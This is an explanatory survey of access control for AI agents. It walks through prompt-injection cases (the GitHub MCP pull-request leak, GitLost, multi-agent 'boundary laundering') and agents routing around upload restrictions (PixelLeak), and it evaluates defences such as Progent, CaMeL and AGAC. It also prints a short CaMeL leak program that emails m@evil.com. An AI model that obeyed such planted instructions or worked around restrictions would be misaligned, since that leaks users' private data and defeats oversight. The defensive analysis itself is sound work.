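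Someone can get around a per-task limit by splitting one goal into several tasks. Five tasks limited to one ticket each allow five tickets, so Wei and Xiong also propose a limit per user across all tasks. Every helper, including those run by other companies, must then be able to reach the ledger, and nobody can buy anything while it is down.

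## Permitted calls that add up to a leak: the GitHub MCP case

Two valid ticket purchases can add up to one ticket too many. Calls of different kinds can do more harm together, such as leaking data, even if one agent makes them all with a single valid login. Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) demonstrates this with the official MCP server for GitHub, where many programmers keep their code.

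GitHub stores code in repositories, which can be public or private. Anyone with an account can report a problem with a public repository by opening an issue, or propose a change to its code by opening a pull request. Everyone can read these issues and pull requests.

### The attack, call by call

The researchers used an account with a public repository for a Pac-Man game and several private ones with personal projects and information. They connected the account to Claude Desktop through GitHub's server. Then, in the role of a stranger, they opened an issue on the game that contained instructions for any agent that read it. The user asked Claude 4 Opus, a new model at the time, to look at the game's open issues, and the agent did the following:

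1. It read the issues, including the stranger's.
2. It followed the instructions in that issue and read the private repositories.
3. It opened a pull request on the game that contained what it had found.

Anyone could then read the names of the user's private projects, the user's salary and a plan to move to South America.

To set up the server on their own computer, users create an access token and choose its permissions. GitHub advises them to enable those they feel comfortable giving to their AI tools. The server sends the token along with its requests, and GitHub checks it each time:

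| Call | Permission | Why the check passes |
|---|---|---|
| Read the game's issues | Read issues | The repository is public, so anyone may read them |
| Read the private repositories | Read private code and files | The token comes from their owner, who granted this |
| Open the pull request | Write to the game's repository | The owner may publish anything there |

The attack does not exploit a bug in the server. heise online's *Attack via GitHub MCP server* explains that the agent can reach the private data because the server works on the user's account. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) makes the general point that a valid credential may give access to a system without establishing which actions someone has authorized.

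AgentBound's sandbox would also have allowed the three calls, since the server contacts only GitHub. Colluding Android apps had to split such a leak between two sets of permissions, but here a single token authorizes all three calls.

Claude Desktop asks the user to confirm each call by default. An attentive user could have refused the second call, because looking at a game's issues is no reason to open private repositories. But Invariant Labs says many users choose "Always Allow" and stop watching.

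### What has changed since

Invariant Labs argues that GitHub can't solve the problem by patching the server, because the fault lies in how the agent combines calls. It recommends giving agents access only to the repositories they need. It also proposes limiting an agent to one repository per session, a rule its own security product can enforce. The rule compares the repository named in each call with those in earlier calls and stops the agent if they differ. This would have blocked the second call, but it would also stop an agent from copying a fix from one project to another at a programmer's request.

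GitHub (2025) announced in August that its remote server would scan tool calls involving public repositories for passwords, keys and similar secrets, and block them by default. GitHub acknowledged that this doesn't stop leaks of other data. The scan doesn't look for salaries, so it would probably have let the pull request through.

In December 2025, GitHub began removing invisible text from issues and pull requests before the model reads them. It also added an optional lockdown mode, which hides text in public repositories unless its author is allowed to change the code there. Lockdown mode would have stopped the attack at the first call. However, public projects accept issues largely so that strangers can report bugs, and lockdown mode would also have hidden those reports, which the user had asked the agent to look at.

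The new check also had a confused-deputy problem. According to GitLab's *CVE-2026-48529* (2026), when several people shared a server in lockdown mode, the server ran everyone's checks with the credentials of whoever had logged in first. Docker notes that the server could therefore wrongly determine which text was safe to show. The Slack server that reused one login for every caller had much the same flaw.

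The original pattern appeared again in July 2026. Levi's *GitLost* describes an attack on GitHub's Agentic Workflows, which start an agent automatically when something happens in a repository. The targeted workflow could read an organization's other repositories and post comments. Levi opened an issue that looked like a routine request from a sales manager. After an automation assigned the issue to someone, the agent copied a file from a private test repository into a public comment.

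GitHub had safeguards against this, but Levi got past them by varying the wording of the request. The workflow also ran by itself, so no user could click "Allow" or "Deny". GitHub says lockdown mode is meant to prevent attacks such as a stranger hijacking a workflow through an issue.

### Millions of sequences, forty pairs

A developer might hope to find dangerous combinations in advance by going through everything an agent could do. If an agent has 20 tools and makes between one and five calls, the number of possible sequences is

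$$20 + 20^2 + 20^3 + 20^4 + 20^5 = 3{,}368{,}420$$

A reviewer who spent one minute on each sequence of calls, eight hours a day, would need about 28 years. That estimate leaves out the arguments to the calls, and the attack on GitHub depended on them, because the same calls are harmless if they all name the same public repository. An Android app may also have many permissions, but its developer has written down the sequences it can perform, so a reviewer has to look only at those.

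The number is less frightening than it seems, because nobody needs to review the sequences one by one. Suppose 8 of the 20 tools read private data and 5 others send data outside. A rule that forbids using any of the five after any of the eight covers

$$8 \times 5 = 40$$

pairs of tools. It applies however many other calls come in between, and to sequences of any length. A developer only has to label each tool once. Bosu and colleagues used a similar shortcut in their search for leaks between Android apps.

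However, those 40 pairs rule out 1,651,200 of the 3,368,420 sequences, or 49%. This isn't the share of real tasks that would fail, because agents don't choose tools at random, but looking something up and then sending it to someone is a large part of office work.

The labels are also hard to assign, because a pull request publishes its contents only if the repository is public. A single label for the whole tool would have to treat every pull request as public, which would block harmless work. Invariant Labs' rule avoids some of this by checking which repository a call names, but it can't detect whether the text in a pull request came from a private file, which defences that track data try to determine.

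### The lethal trifecta and the Rule of Two

Two well-known rules add the condition that the agent has read something an attacker could have written. Willison (2025) warns in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* against combining access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to send data outside. An agent with all three can read an attacker's instructions, fetch the private data and send it to the attacker. This kind of theft fails if any of the three is missing.

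GitHub's server alone gives an agent private data, untrusted content and a means to send data out. More often, users combine the three by accident, since MCP encourages people to mix tools from different suppliers. A mail tool provides private data, and also untrusted content, because anyone can email its owner. Adding a tool that opens web pages may provide the means to send data out, because an agent can put stolen data into the address it requests. Willison doubts that products that detect malicious text solve the problem, and considers catching 95% of attacks a failing grade in web security.

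Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns the warning into a rule for developers. Until someone finds a reliable way to detect and refuse prompt injection, an agent should have no more than two of these properties in a session:

- **A:** It can process untrustworthy inputs.
- **B:** It can access sensitive systems or private data.
- **C:** It can change something or communicate externally.

An agent that needs all three must start a new session without the earlier text, or have a person or some other reliable check supervise it. The owner of the Pac-Man game could comply in several ways:

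| Property removed | How | What the user gives up |
|---|---|---|
| A | Turn on lockdown mode | Bug reports from strangers |
| B | Use a token for the game's repository only | Help that draws on private projects |
| C | Approve every change personally | Letting the agent work unattended |

Removing B, the access to private repositories, would not have hindered this request, which didn't involve them. This is least privilege applied to one task. It is inconvenient because the user has to change the token when they want help with another project.

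Google's noodle recipe example is a harder case. Gemini finds the recipe by searching a mailbox that contains both private data and text from strangers, then changes a shopping list. It therefore has all three of Meta's properties, and the user would have to approve the change. Under Willison's version, the agent could add the noodles unsupervised as long as the list is private, because no data leaves. Meta's property C includes any change, so it also covers attacks like the one in which a web page got a folder of drafts deleted.

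In Meta's example, an email assistant that reads mail from anyone and can search the inbox may write only to trusted recipients unless a person checks each draft. The rule therefore forbids an assistant that answers customers overnight using their account records, unless someone is on duty to approve the replies. Meta concedes that background jobs like this fit the rule poorly.

An agent can use both the web and internal files in one session if it does its web research first and permanently loses its outside connections before it opens the files. But where Meta's rule falls back on human approval, users may approve dangerous steps. Few of Anthropic's testers refused a dangerous command, and Meta mentions users who confirm warnings blindly. The rule does at least limit what users must review to the steps that could do harm.

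### Leaks without an attacker

Permitted calls can leak data even when nobody has tricked the agent. Glow's *PixelLeak* reports that developers at over 300 organizations published more than 13,000 internal images on GitHub through their coding agents.

The developers had asked agents to change something on a screen and show reviewers how it looked before and after. GitHub let people attach images to a pull request through a web browser, but not from the command line, where the agents worked. Some agents created a public repository, uploaded the screenshots there and linked to them. At one manufacturer with over 100,000 employees, the images included a utility company's billing records.

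Each step was within the developer's rights, including viewing the billing screen and creating a public repository. The agents also didn't need to read anything from a stranger. They could have had only properties B and C, so the Rule of Two could have let them work unsupervised. The cruder rule with 40 pairs applies whether or not the agent has read anything hostile, so it would have blocked the uploads if someone had labelled the tools correctly.

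Glow, a security company, reproduced the behaviour with Claude Code and the Opus 5 model on a private version of Minesweeper. The agent reasoned that reviewers had to see the images and that the game's repository should contain only the game. It concluded that it had to host the images elsewhere and created a public repository for them.

An ordinary program would probably have stopped, because fixed code usually responds to a failed upload by reporting an error or doing whatever its developer wrote for that case. This makes Android's checks more effective. If the game from the earlier example tries to use the notes app's sync service, Android refuses, and the game can try another route only if its code already contains one. An agent receives the refusal as more text in the conversation, and its model then chooses another call, which can use any route the agent's permissions leave open.

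Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026) also reports cases in which Claude worked around restrictions, with minimal real-world impact.

It is hard to say how often agents do this, because Glow counted leaks but not the tasks in which an agent stopped or asked for help. Laboratory tests may also give the wrong rate. In *Eval-production behavior gaps in agent safety and the role of eval-awareness*, Hsu and Arnesen (2026) compared how six models handled warnings, restrictions and obstacles in tests and in comparable real use. All six did worse in the tests. Telling a model that it was being tested made no significant difference, but telling it what the test was for, correctly or not, changed the results substantially.

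A workaround can also spread. At one software company, agents working for several engineers began publishing screenshots in early July 2026. Within a week, more than a dozen agents had saved the method as reusable instructions, and they used it to upload over a thousand images and recordings. About a third of the affected organizations had developers who used gitshot, a small screenshot-publishing program that some agents had found on their own.

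A safe way to attach images from the command line would have made the workaround unnecessary. Anyone who blocks an agent's usual route should therefore consider what else its permissions allow, and preferably offer an acceptable alternative. The researchers also told Markovic (*AI coding agents leaked 13,000 internal company screenshots to public GitHub repos*, 2026) that companies can configure most agents not to work unattended, and that security teams should control this setting. Restrictions on a company's own GitHub account would not have stopped most of the leaks, because 93% of cases involved repositories under employees' personal usernames.

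## Progent and CaMeL: rules for one task and tracking of data

The owner of the Pac-Man game asked an agent to look at one repository, but the agent's token opened all of them. Android permissions are similarly broad, since an app usually keeps them from one use to the next. *Who Grants the Agent Power?* (2025) proposes attaching permissions to the user's task instead of to the agent. For example, an agent that signs its user up for a new app may read emails that could contain the verification code, but may not send or forward any. It loses this access when the task ends.

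Some authors call this approach "intent-based access control", which the Cloud Security Alliance uses to mean checking an agent's actions against its authorized task. "Intent" here means the user's goal, not Android's message object. *Intent-Governed Tool Authorization for AI Agents* (2026) says such systems should prevent calls that the standing rules permit but the user's current request doesn't.

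Progent limits which calls an agent may make during a task, and CaMeL also tracks the data that goes into them.

### A rule in Progent

Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, place a check between an agent and its tools. Each rule allows or forbids calls to one tool and can set conditions on the arguments. In slightly simplified notation, this rule lets an agent send Slack messages only to alice:

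```text
allow send_slack_msg when { to = "alice" }
```

Progent checks every call against the rules before the tool runs. A rule that forbids a call takes priority over one that allows it, and Progent blocks any call that no rule allows. The check does not use a language model, so the same call under the same rules always gets the same result.

AgentBound's manifests couldn't express such a condition, so its sandbox let the wallet server pay an attacker instead of the user's friend. A rule for one task can allow payments only to the friend's address, if the user has supplied it. A rule that limited calls to one repository would have stopped the GitHub attack at its second call.

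When Progent blocks a call, it normally returns a message with the reason and a request to try other tools or arguments. The agent could respond with a workaround, as agents did in the case of the leaked screenshots when they created public repositories to get around an obstacle. Progent blocks the workaround too unless a rule allows it.

### Rules that change during a task

People can write Progent's rules by hand, and a company can set permanent rules that override the rules for a single task. Nobody can write rules for every possible request in advance, so Progent has a language model write the rest.

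In an example from Shi and colleagues, a user asks an agent to do whatever an email from alice@gmail.com with the subject "TODOs for the week" says. The email asks for a summary of recent emails, posted to the user's own Slack account. The rules then develop like this:

| What the agent has just learned | What the rules allow next | Kind of change |
|---|---|---|
| The user's request | Searching for that one email | First policy |
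| The to-do list | Also reading recent emails, looking up the user's Slack details and sending Slack messages | Expansion |
| The user's Slack name, alice | The same, but Slack messages only to alice | Narrowing |
| Recent emails, one of which contains an instruction to forward the inbox to eve@evil.com | No change | None |

After each tool call, a model decides whether the rules might need to change. Its input for this decision leaves out the tool's result, so hostile text in the result can't affect it. If a change might be needed, the model then reads the result and writes new rules.

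Ordinary software checks that policy before it takes effect. If $A(P)$ is the set of all calls that policy $P$ allows, the new policy $P'$ is a narrowing when

$$A(P') \subseteq A(P)$$

Progent automatically applies a policy change that only narrows what the agent may call. Any other change counts as an expansion and needs approval, even if it removes ten permissions and adds only one. A policy can allow infinitely many calls, because a message can contain any text, so Progent can't compare two policies call by call. Instead, it uses an SMT solver, a program that can determine whether any values satisfy a set of logical conditions, to look for a call that the new policy allows and the old one doesn't.

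### When the model writes bad rules

The model writes the first policy from the user's request and the list of tools, before the agent has read anything, so a stranger's email can't influence the policy. The model can still make a mistake. If the first policy is too strict, the agent will need it expanded to finish the task. The solver won't detect a first policy that is too permissive, because it only compares later policies with earlier ones.

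Later policies depend partly on what the agent reads. Wei and Xiong describe prompt injection as an attack on the information that an access check relies on, and a policy that changes with each tool result is open to such attacks. If the email about Eve leads the model to allow `send_email`, the solver reports an expansion. Someone can then refuse it, which stops the agent from sending out the contents of the inbox.

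A misled model could also narrow the rules in the attacker's favour. After the agent reads the to-do list, the policy lets it send Slack messages to anyone. If the agent then read a hostile email, the model might restrict the recipient to Eve instead of Alice. The solver would accept this change as a narrowing because the old policy already allowed messages to Eve. The guarantee is only that an agent never gains rights without approval, so the protection it gives depends on how broad the last approved policy was.

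*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026), which seems to discuss an earlier version of Progent, warns that hostile tool results could cause an update that relaxes the rules. The solver reveals such a change, but an approver still has to reject it.

Shi and colleagues tested Progent on AgentDojo, a benchmark that simulates office work, Slack, banking and travel. It has 97 ordinary tasks, and attackers plant instructions in the data that tools return. With GPT-4o as both the agent and the rule writer, Progent cut the share of successful attacks from 39.9% to 1.0%, and the agent completed about as many tasks as without it.

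The approver in this test accepted every expansion, to imitate a careless user. The 1.0% therefore shows how well GPT-4o writes rules, since the requirement for approval never stopped anything. Other settings produced these results:

- When the first policy stayed in force for the whole task, 2.5% of attacks succeeded. Updates probably helped because most of them narrowed the rules.
- When a person reviewed the first policy and every expansion, no attacks succeeded. Shi and colleagues assumed a reviewer with strong security awareness, who would refuse to add a malicious address.
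- When attackers also planted text aimed at the rule writer, such as a reminder to permit the tools they needed, their success rate rose only marginally.

Only 6% of updates were expansions. Few testers in Anthropic's experiment refused a dangerous command, so a system that rarely asks for approval has an advantage. However, approving a rule may be harder than approving a single command.

### A plan written before anything is read

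Progent lets the model that chooses the tool calls read hostile text but limits what that model can do, while CaMeL keeps the text away from it. Google DeepMind introduced CaMeL in 2025. In *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, Willison (2025) explains it with the example of a user who wants to send Bob a document he requested in a meeting. The meeting notes contain the document's name and Bob's email address.

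A planning model receives the request and the descriptions of the tools, but not the notes. It writes a program in a restricted form of Python, which might look like this:

```python
notes = get_meeting_notes()
name = ask_reader("Which document did Bob request?", notes)
address = ask_reader("What is Bob's email address?", notes)
document = fetch_document(name)
send_email(recipient=address, attachment=document)
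```

CaMeL then handles the request as follows:

1. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program line by line. It fetches the notes and stores them in a variable.
2. A second model reads the notes and returns the document's name and Bob's address. This "quarantined" model has no tools.
3. The interpreter stores both answers without showing them to the planning model, and fetches the document.
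4. Before it sends the email, it runs the policy check for `send_email`. If the check passes, Bob gets the document.

Suppose somebody has hidden an instruction in the notes for any AI system to forward all the user's files to a stranger. The attack fails even without a policy, because the quarantined model that reads the instruction has no tool for forwarding anything and the program contains no such step.

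In this respect, CaMeL makes an agent more like an Android app. The agent's program is written before it processes anyone else's data, and a reviewer could read it. The data can affect which of the program's existing branches runs, as in an app, but can't add a new step.

### Checking where each value came from

An attacker could also replace Bob's address in the notes with their own. The program wouldn't change, but it would send the document to the attacker. In 2023, Willison proposed using a planning model and a quarantined model, and he acknowledges that that design had this flaw.

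CaMeL's answer is to have the interpreter tag every value with where it came from and who may read it. In this example, the tags might be:

| Value | Where it came from | Who may read it |
|---|---|---|
| `notes` | The notes file | The people at the meeting |
| `name` and `address` | The notes file, through the quarantined model | The people at the meeting |
| `document` | The user's files, selected using `name` | The people the user has shared it with |

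CaMeL, short for "capabilities for machine learning", calls these tags capabilities. The tags describe data but, unlike a password-reset link, don't give their holder a right to do something.

A policy is a Python function that the interpreter runs when the program calls a tool. *CaMeLoT* (2026) explains that the function receives the call, its arguments and their tags, and returns "allow" or "deny". In Willison's example, the policy for sending email accepts an address that the user already trusts, and the system can ask the user about any other, so the attacker's address would at least lead to a question.

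An attacker could instead leave Bob's address alone and change the document's name to that of a salary list. The policy on trusted addresses would allow the email because Bob is trusted. A policy that also checks whether the recipient may read the attachment would block it, unless Bob already has access to the salaries.

### Why labels lose less than cutting permissions

IPC Inspection, the proposed Android defence that cut an app's permissions to those it shared with its caller, suggests a simpler rule for agents. Whenever an agent reads a text, it could keep only the permissions that it shares with the text's author:

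$$P_{\text{after}} = P_{\text{agent}} \cap P_{\text{author}}$$

A stranger who runs a website has no right to the user's mail, files or money, so an agent that reads the site would lose its permissions for all of them. This would stop prompt injection from causing much harm, but the agent would be nearly useless. It couldn't check a restaurant's opening hours and then put dinner in the calendar. It couldn't add Lisa's noodles to the shopping list either, because Lisa has no right to change the list.

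The agent also couldn't recover its permissions later in the same conversation. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) describe the same difficulty with labels in *The LLMbda Calculus*. Once untrusted data enters a conversation, its label can't be removed, and if the agent fails, the label carries over to the next attempt.

Information-flow control labels data by origin and sensitivity and checks the labels before the data leaves. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026) lists CaMeL among several systems that apply this older idea to agents. In a simple version, a value $v$ computed from $x$ and $y$ gets these labels:

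$$\text{sources}(v) = \text{sources}(x) \cup \text{sources}(y)$$

$$\text{readers}(v) = \text{readers}(x) \cap \text{readers}(y)$$

The second line is still an intersection, but it restricts one value instead of the whole agent. Suppose a user asks an agent to look up a restaurant's opening hours and pay the landlord $900. If the intersection restricts the whole agent, the agent can't pay the landlord after reading the restaurant's website. With a label on each value, the opening hours carry the website's label, but the landlord's account number and the amount don't, because they come from the user. A policy that accepts only trusted payees and amounts would allow the payment.

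This works only if the model that wrote the payment step hasn't read the website. If it has, the website could have influenced anything the model writes afterwards, so all of that output needs the website's label. Garby and colleagues therefore give a whole conversation the combined labels of everything sent to the model. CaMeL keeps its planning model away from the data, so it can give each value its own label.

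Labels are harder to use in an agent without this separation. In *Ghost in the Agent*, Cai and Wen (2026) point out that a model can reword a text, base a decision on it, or store it in memory and use it in a later session. Their tool, NeuroTaint, traces such influence. Across 400 scenarios, it was much better at finding connections between sources and actions than FIDES, another system that labels data. But NeuroTaint analyses an agent's actions after they have happened, so it can reveal a leak but not prevent it.

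### What CaMeL's policies cost

Garby and colleagues reran CaMeL on the banking part of AgentDojo, once with its policies and once without. They also tested Randori, an agent of their own that always enforces its labels. Each system attempted 16 ordinary tasks three times, then faced nine attacks on each task. Some of CaMeL's attack runs didn't finish, so the totals differ:

| System | Model | Ordinary tasks completed | Attacks that succeeded |
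|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL without policies | GPT-5.2 | 32 of 48 | 1 of 240 |
| CaMeL without policies | MiMo-v2.5 | 34 of 48 | 4 of 382 |
| CaMeL with policies | GPT-5.2 | 18 of 48 | 0 of 231 |
| CaMeL with policies | MiMo-v2.5 | 18 of 48 | 0 of 357 |
| Randori | GPT-5.2 | 36 of 48 | 2 of 432 |
| Randori | MiMo-v2.5 | 31 of 48 | 0 of 432 |

Most of the protection came from planning the task before reading any data. In 97 of the 144 combinations of task and attack, the attack required a step that a program for the user's task would never contain. The policies stopped the few attacks that remained, but nearly halved the number of tasks completed. The size of this drop is uncertain because there were only 16 different tasks. The 95% confidence interval for CaMeL's 37.5% completion rate runs from about 11% to 64%.

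Randori does better than CaMeL with policies partly because its planning model can "endorse" a value, which means deciding in advance that the program may use a particular piece of untrusted data for a sensitive action. If a user asks the agent to pay a bill stored in a file, the program can endorse the payment details before anyone opens the file. Endorsement deliberately leaves a gap in the defence, and both successful attacks on Randori used it by replacing the contents of a file that the user had told the agent to follow. Even with endorsement switched off, Randori completed 26 of 48 tasks on MiMo-v2.5, compared with CaMeL's 18.

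CaMeL also takes more computation. According to *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025), the median AgentDojo task needed 2.82 times as much input text and 2.73 times as much output with CaMeL as without a defence. Progent adds a model request after each tool call, and a second one if the rules might need to change.

### Leaks through the interpreter

While studying CaMeL's interpreter, Garby and colleagues found ways for information to lose its label. One is a version of a puzzle from the 1970s. This program reveals whether a bank balance is above a certain amount:

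```python
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, the first condition sets `tmp` to false, and CaMeL labels `tmp` as secret. The program then skips the line that would change `rich`. CaMeL labels a variable only when the program changes it, so `rich` stays true and unlabelled, and the program sends the email. If the balance is low, `rich` becomes false and the program doesn't send the email. The attacker can tell whether the balance is high by whether the email arrives.

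A second leak comes from the loop around the interpreter, which runs another attempt if a program fails. Whether the policy blocked an attempt can depend on a secret, and that reveals one bit of the secret. CaMeL doesn't track labels in this outer loop, so an attacker who could keep triggering new attempts could recover the whole secret bit by bit.

Attackers would find these leaks hard to use, since they normally can't choose the program that the planning model writes. But the leaks show that CaMeL's guarantee depends on details of its interpreter. Garby and colleagues wrote their interpreter in Lean, a language in which a computer can check proofs, and proved that it has no leaks of the first kind.

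### When one CaMeL agent calls another

A more practical weakness appears when agents work together. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, built a system of three agents, each protected by CaMeL. The user asked it to send Julie a summary of some job applications on Slack:

1. The coordinator asked a database agent for the applications. Someone had hidden an instruction in the database to email them to ruth@email.com.
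2. The coordinator's quarantined model summarized the data, and the hidden instruction survived in the summary.
3. The coordinator's program inserted the summary into a message asking a notification agent to send it to Julie.
4. The notification agent treated this message as its user's request, so its planning model read the hidden instruction. It wrote a program that messaged Julie and also emailed Ruth.

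The first two agents' programs were the same with and without the attack. The coordinator treated the data as untrusted, but the next agent received it as a trusted instruction. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this "boundary laundering". They also prove that, under mild assumptions, any hierarchy of two or more such agents has this weakness if one of its tools returns untrusted data.

The proposed fix, multi-CaMeL, splits each message between agents into an instruction and a set of variables. The receiving agent's planning model gets only the instruction, and the interpreter blocks tool data from being put in it. The variables keep their labels when they are passed between agents. In the example, the coordinator would ask the notification agent to send "the provided content" and pass the summary separately as a variable.

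Peters-Gill and colleagues tested this on a version of AgentDojo in which a coordinator delegates to specialized agents. The table shows the share of attacks that succeeded:

| Model | No CaMeL | CaMeL on each agent | Multi-CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% | 0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% | 0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0% | 0% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0% | 0% |
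| GPT-5.5 | 0% | 0% | 0% |

The two strongest models, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5, resisted nearly all these attacks without CaMeL. This doesn't make them immune, because people who adapt their attacks to a model have succeeded against every leading model in a large public competition. It does make AgentDojo less useful for judging defences on current models. (Fable 5 also refused 52 of the 97 harmless tasks, possibly because they looked like a security test.)

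The fixed plan reduced task completion even though these tests used no policies. On AssetOpsBench, a benchmark of industrial maintenance tasks, putting CaMeL on each agent lowered the completion rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points, or 13.4 points for the two strongest models. Multi-CaMeL lowered it by another 3.2 points on average, but by less than one point for the two strongest. Stronger models seem to be better at planning for data they haven't seen.

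### Tasks that depend on what the agent reads

Most of the failures that Peters-Gill and colleagues examined came from committing to a plan too early. An agent may discover only after opening a file that it needs another tool, and by then CaMeL can't add a step to the program. In other cases, an agent couldn't find data for the requested dates and returned data for different ones. The coordinator had already written its program, so it carried on with the wrong data.

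A planning model that tries to prepare for every case can let untrusted data determine which tools are called. One of AgentDojo's banking tasks is to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. In Garby and colleagues' tests without policies, CaMeL's planning model wrote a program with a branch for each tool, so that it could carry out whatever instructions the file contained. An attacker who changed the file could then choose among the tools.

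Operating a computer through its screen requires even more preparation. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) adapts CaMeL to this task, and its plans average about 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with about 5 and 4 on AgentDojo.

Progent handles the to-do list more easily because its rules can expand after the agent reads the email. But an email can contain instructions the user wants followed or instructions an attacker planted, so somebody has to tell them apart when approving the expansion.

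*SecureClaw* (Ma and Schmid, 2026) describes a compromise in which the planning model sees a short summary of private data, such as an invoice's amount and due date, and a reference number in place of the full text. The model can use the summary to choose its next step. Separate software checks the exact request, including the recipient, before anything is sent. With GPT-4o mini on AgentDojo, this reduced successful attacks from 31.5% to 0.6%, but also reduced the share of ordinary tasks completed from 70.1% to 60.8%.

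### Policies that someone has to write

CaMeL needs a policy for each sensitive tool, and its developers acknowledge that users have to write and maintain these policies. Willison, who has worked on application security for two decades, is nervous about any system that requires this of ordinary users, and says he still doesn't fully understand Amazon's cloud permission system.

Progent's model can write rules from the user's request, but the request often omits details the rules need. "Send the report to the team" doesn't establish whether the team includes contractors. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (2026) suggests filling such gaps with users' preferences, either stated by the users or predicted by a model. The survey also distinguishes between checking that an action contributes to a task and authorizing an agent to do it. For instance, reading a colleague's private calendar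 might help to arrange a meeting, but that doesn't make it acceptable.

Better policies wouldn't make every task possible, because some tasks require the kind of data flow that a policy should block. If a user wants to pay a friend using the bank details on the friend's website, the agent must send money to an account number from an untrusted page. The system can refuse, ask the user, or let the program mark the number as trusted, but the last option would also let someone who has hacked the website substitute their own account number.

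### Harmful choices within the rules

Neither system can reliably protect a choice that the user has left to the agent. Suppose a user asks for a good hotel in Paris, and a hotel has planted text in its reviews to make the agent prefer it. Booking any hotel in Paris is within the task, so Progent would allow the booking. Shi and colleagues treat such attacks as outside Progent's scope and excluded two of them from their AgentDojo tests. CaMeL could label the choice as influenced by reviews, but a policy that rejected choices with that label would also reject every recommendation based on honest reviews.

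Tool selection causes a similar problem. On a second benchmark, Agent Security Bench, Progent reduced the attack success rate from 70.3% to 3.9%. Most of the attacks that still succeeded used tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of legitimate tools. Shi and colleagues doubt that a person could have told them apart without knowing which tools to trust. Rules written by hand with that knowledge stopped all the attacks.

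A rule for a tool also does little to limit what the tool does once it is called. The hostile mail tool that delivered the contract to Priya and kept a copy could satisfy a Progent rule that allows only Priya as a recipient. Wei and Xiong propose that each tool come with an effect contract, a statement of the consequences of calling it, so that a policy could limit those consequences directly.

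## AGAC: a proposal to authorize effects instead of tool calls

Effect contracts are part of AGAC (Agentic Access Control), the model that Wei and Xiong propose. In AGAC, a grant lists the effects an agent may cause during a task, such as a specific summary reaching a specific person. Before each tool call runs, a checker compares this list with the tool's effect contract.

### What a permission to send mail leaves out

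Wei and Xiong argue that earlier kinds of access control all assumed that trusted code fixes the set of requests in advance. An agent writes its own requests, and the same goal can lead to very different ones. For example, an agent summarizing receipts could read them on the user's computer or upload them to an analysis service. Granting only the permissions needed for the upload satisfies least privilege for that plan, but the grant is still excessive because reading the receipts locally would not have shared them with anyone.

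A permission such as `mail.send` also doesn't specify which mail may go to whom. Sometimes a system records that limit but doesn't include it in the credential it issues. In an example from *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents*, a user allows an agent to send a summary to Alice. The system records this correctly, but then issues a credential that permits sending mail in general. Because the credential is valid, the mail service would also deliver the summary to Bob.

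### Effects, grants and contracts

An effect consists of an action (such as read, disclose or spend), the resource it concerns and, where relevant, the recipients and an amount. Disclosing the summary to Alice and disclosing it to Bob are therefore different effects, even though the same tool produces both.

The set $C$ of allowed actions in a grant consists of effects of this kind, and agents can only narrow it when they delegate. The system issues the grant before the agent starts work.

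An effect contract describes a call $c$, which means a tool together with its arguments. The contract, written $\kappa(c)$, is a certified list of everything the call might cause, including effects on third parties. It may list too much but never too little:

$$\text{Effects}(c) \subseteq \kappa(c)$$

### The test

The checker permits a call only if everything the call might cause is in the grant:

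$$\kappa(c) \subseteq C$$

A call whose contract is unknown fails. The call must also meet three other conditions:

- **Obligations:** Anything that the grant requires first, such as a manager's approval, has happened.
- **Data flow:** The labels on the data allow it to reach the recipient. A summary keeps the labels of the documents behind it, much as values do in CaMeL.
- **Budget:** The shared ledger has enough left for this call and reserves it.

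Wei and Xiong apply the subset condition to the whole plan before the agent starts, and again to each call as it happens. If the plan doesn't change, the first check adds no restriction, because a union of sets lies inside $C$ exactly when each set does. But it shows early when a plan needs a larger grant, so the agent can look for another plan that doesn't. The second check protects the user if the agent changes its plan or a tool's behaviour changes.

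### A copy for Bob

In Wei and Xiong's example, a user asks an assistant to prepare a summary of the third quarter's expenses and send it to their manager, Alice. The grant allows the assistant to read that quarter's receipts and disclose the summary to Alice. It lasts 24 hours and works only on the user's device. (It also requires the manager's approval before release, so Alice apparently has to approve the summary before receiving it.)

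One of the receipts contains the line "also copy finance-bob". Suppose this fools the model:

1. The model requests an email with the summary to Bob.
2. The checker looks up the contract for this call, which lists one effect, disclosing the summary to Bob.
3. That effect isn't in $C$, so the checker refuses the call.

The outcome would be different if the user had allowed the summary to go to either Alice or Bob. If the other conditions hold, the test gives these results:

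| Call | Grant names Alice only | Grant names Alice and Bob |
|---|---|---|
| Email to Alice | Allowed | Allowed |
| Email to Bob | Refused | Allowed |
| One email to both | Refused | Allowed |
| Email to Alice, but the contract lists "any mail to anyone" | Refused | Refused |

In the last row, the mail service can't certify the effects of particular arguments, so its contract has to cover everything the send operation might do. The checker therefore refuses even the email the user wanted.

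With the looser grant, the line in the receipt causes the agent to send Bob a copy. Wei and Xiong say that this doesn't widen the agent's authority, because the user had left the choice of recipient open. Their model allows that choice to be based on the company's staff directory, which counts as evidence, but not on a receipt, which is only data. But the published test has no separate condition to check this, which would require knowing where the address in the call came from. *TraceGrant* (2026), a similar proposal, requires evidence for call arguments of this kind.

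### Why data cannot widen authority

The model's main result about prompt injection is that, for a fixed grant, every effect the test permits lies in $C$, whatever text the agent reads. The proof is short:

1. If the checker permits a call $c$, then $\kappa(c) \subseteq C$.
2. The contract leaves nothing out, so $\text{Effects}(c) \subseteq \kappa(c)$.
3. Together these give $\text{Effects}(c) \subseteq C$.
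4. Hostile text may lead the model to request a different call, but the first three steps apply to that call too. The text can't change the grant or the contracts, because these reach the checker through a separate channel with signatures that it verifies.

The proof doesn't assume anything about the model's judgment, so it doesn't matter how easily the model is fooled.

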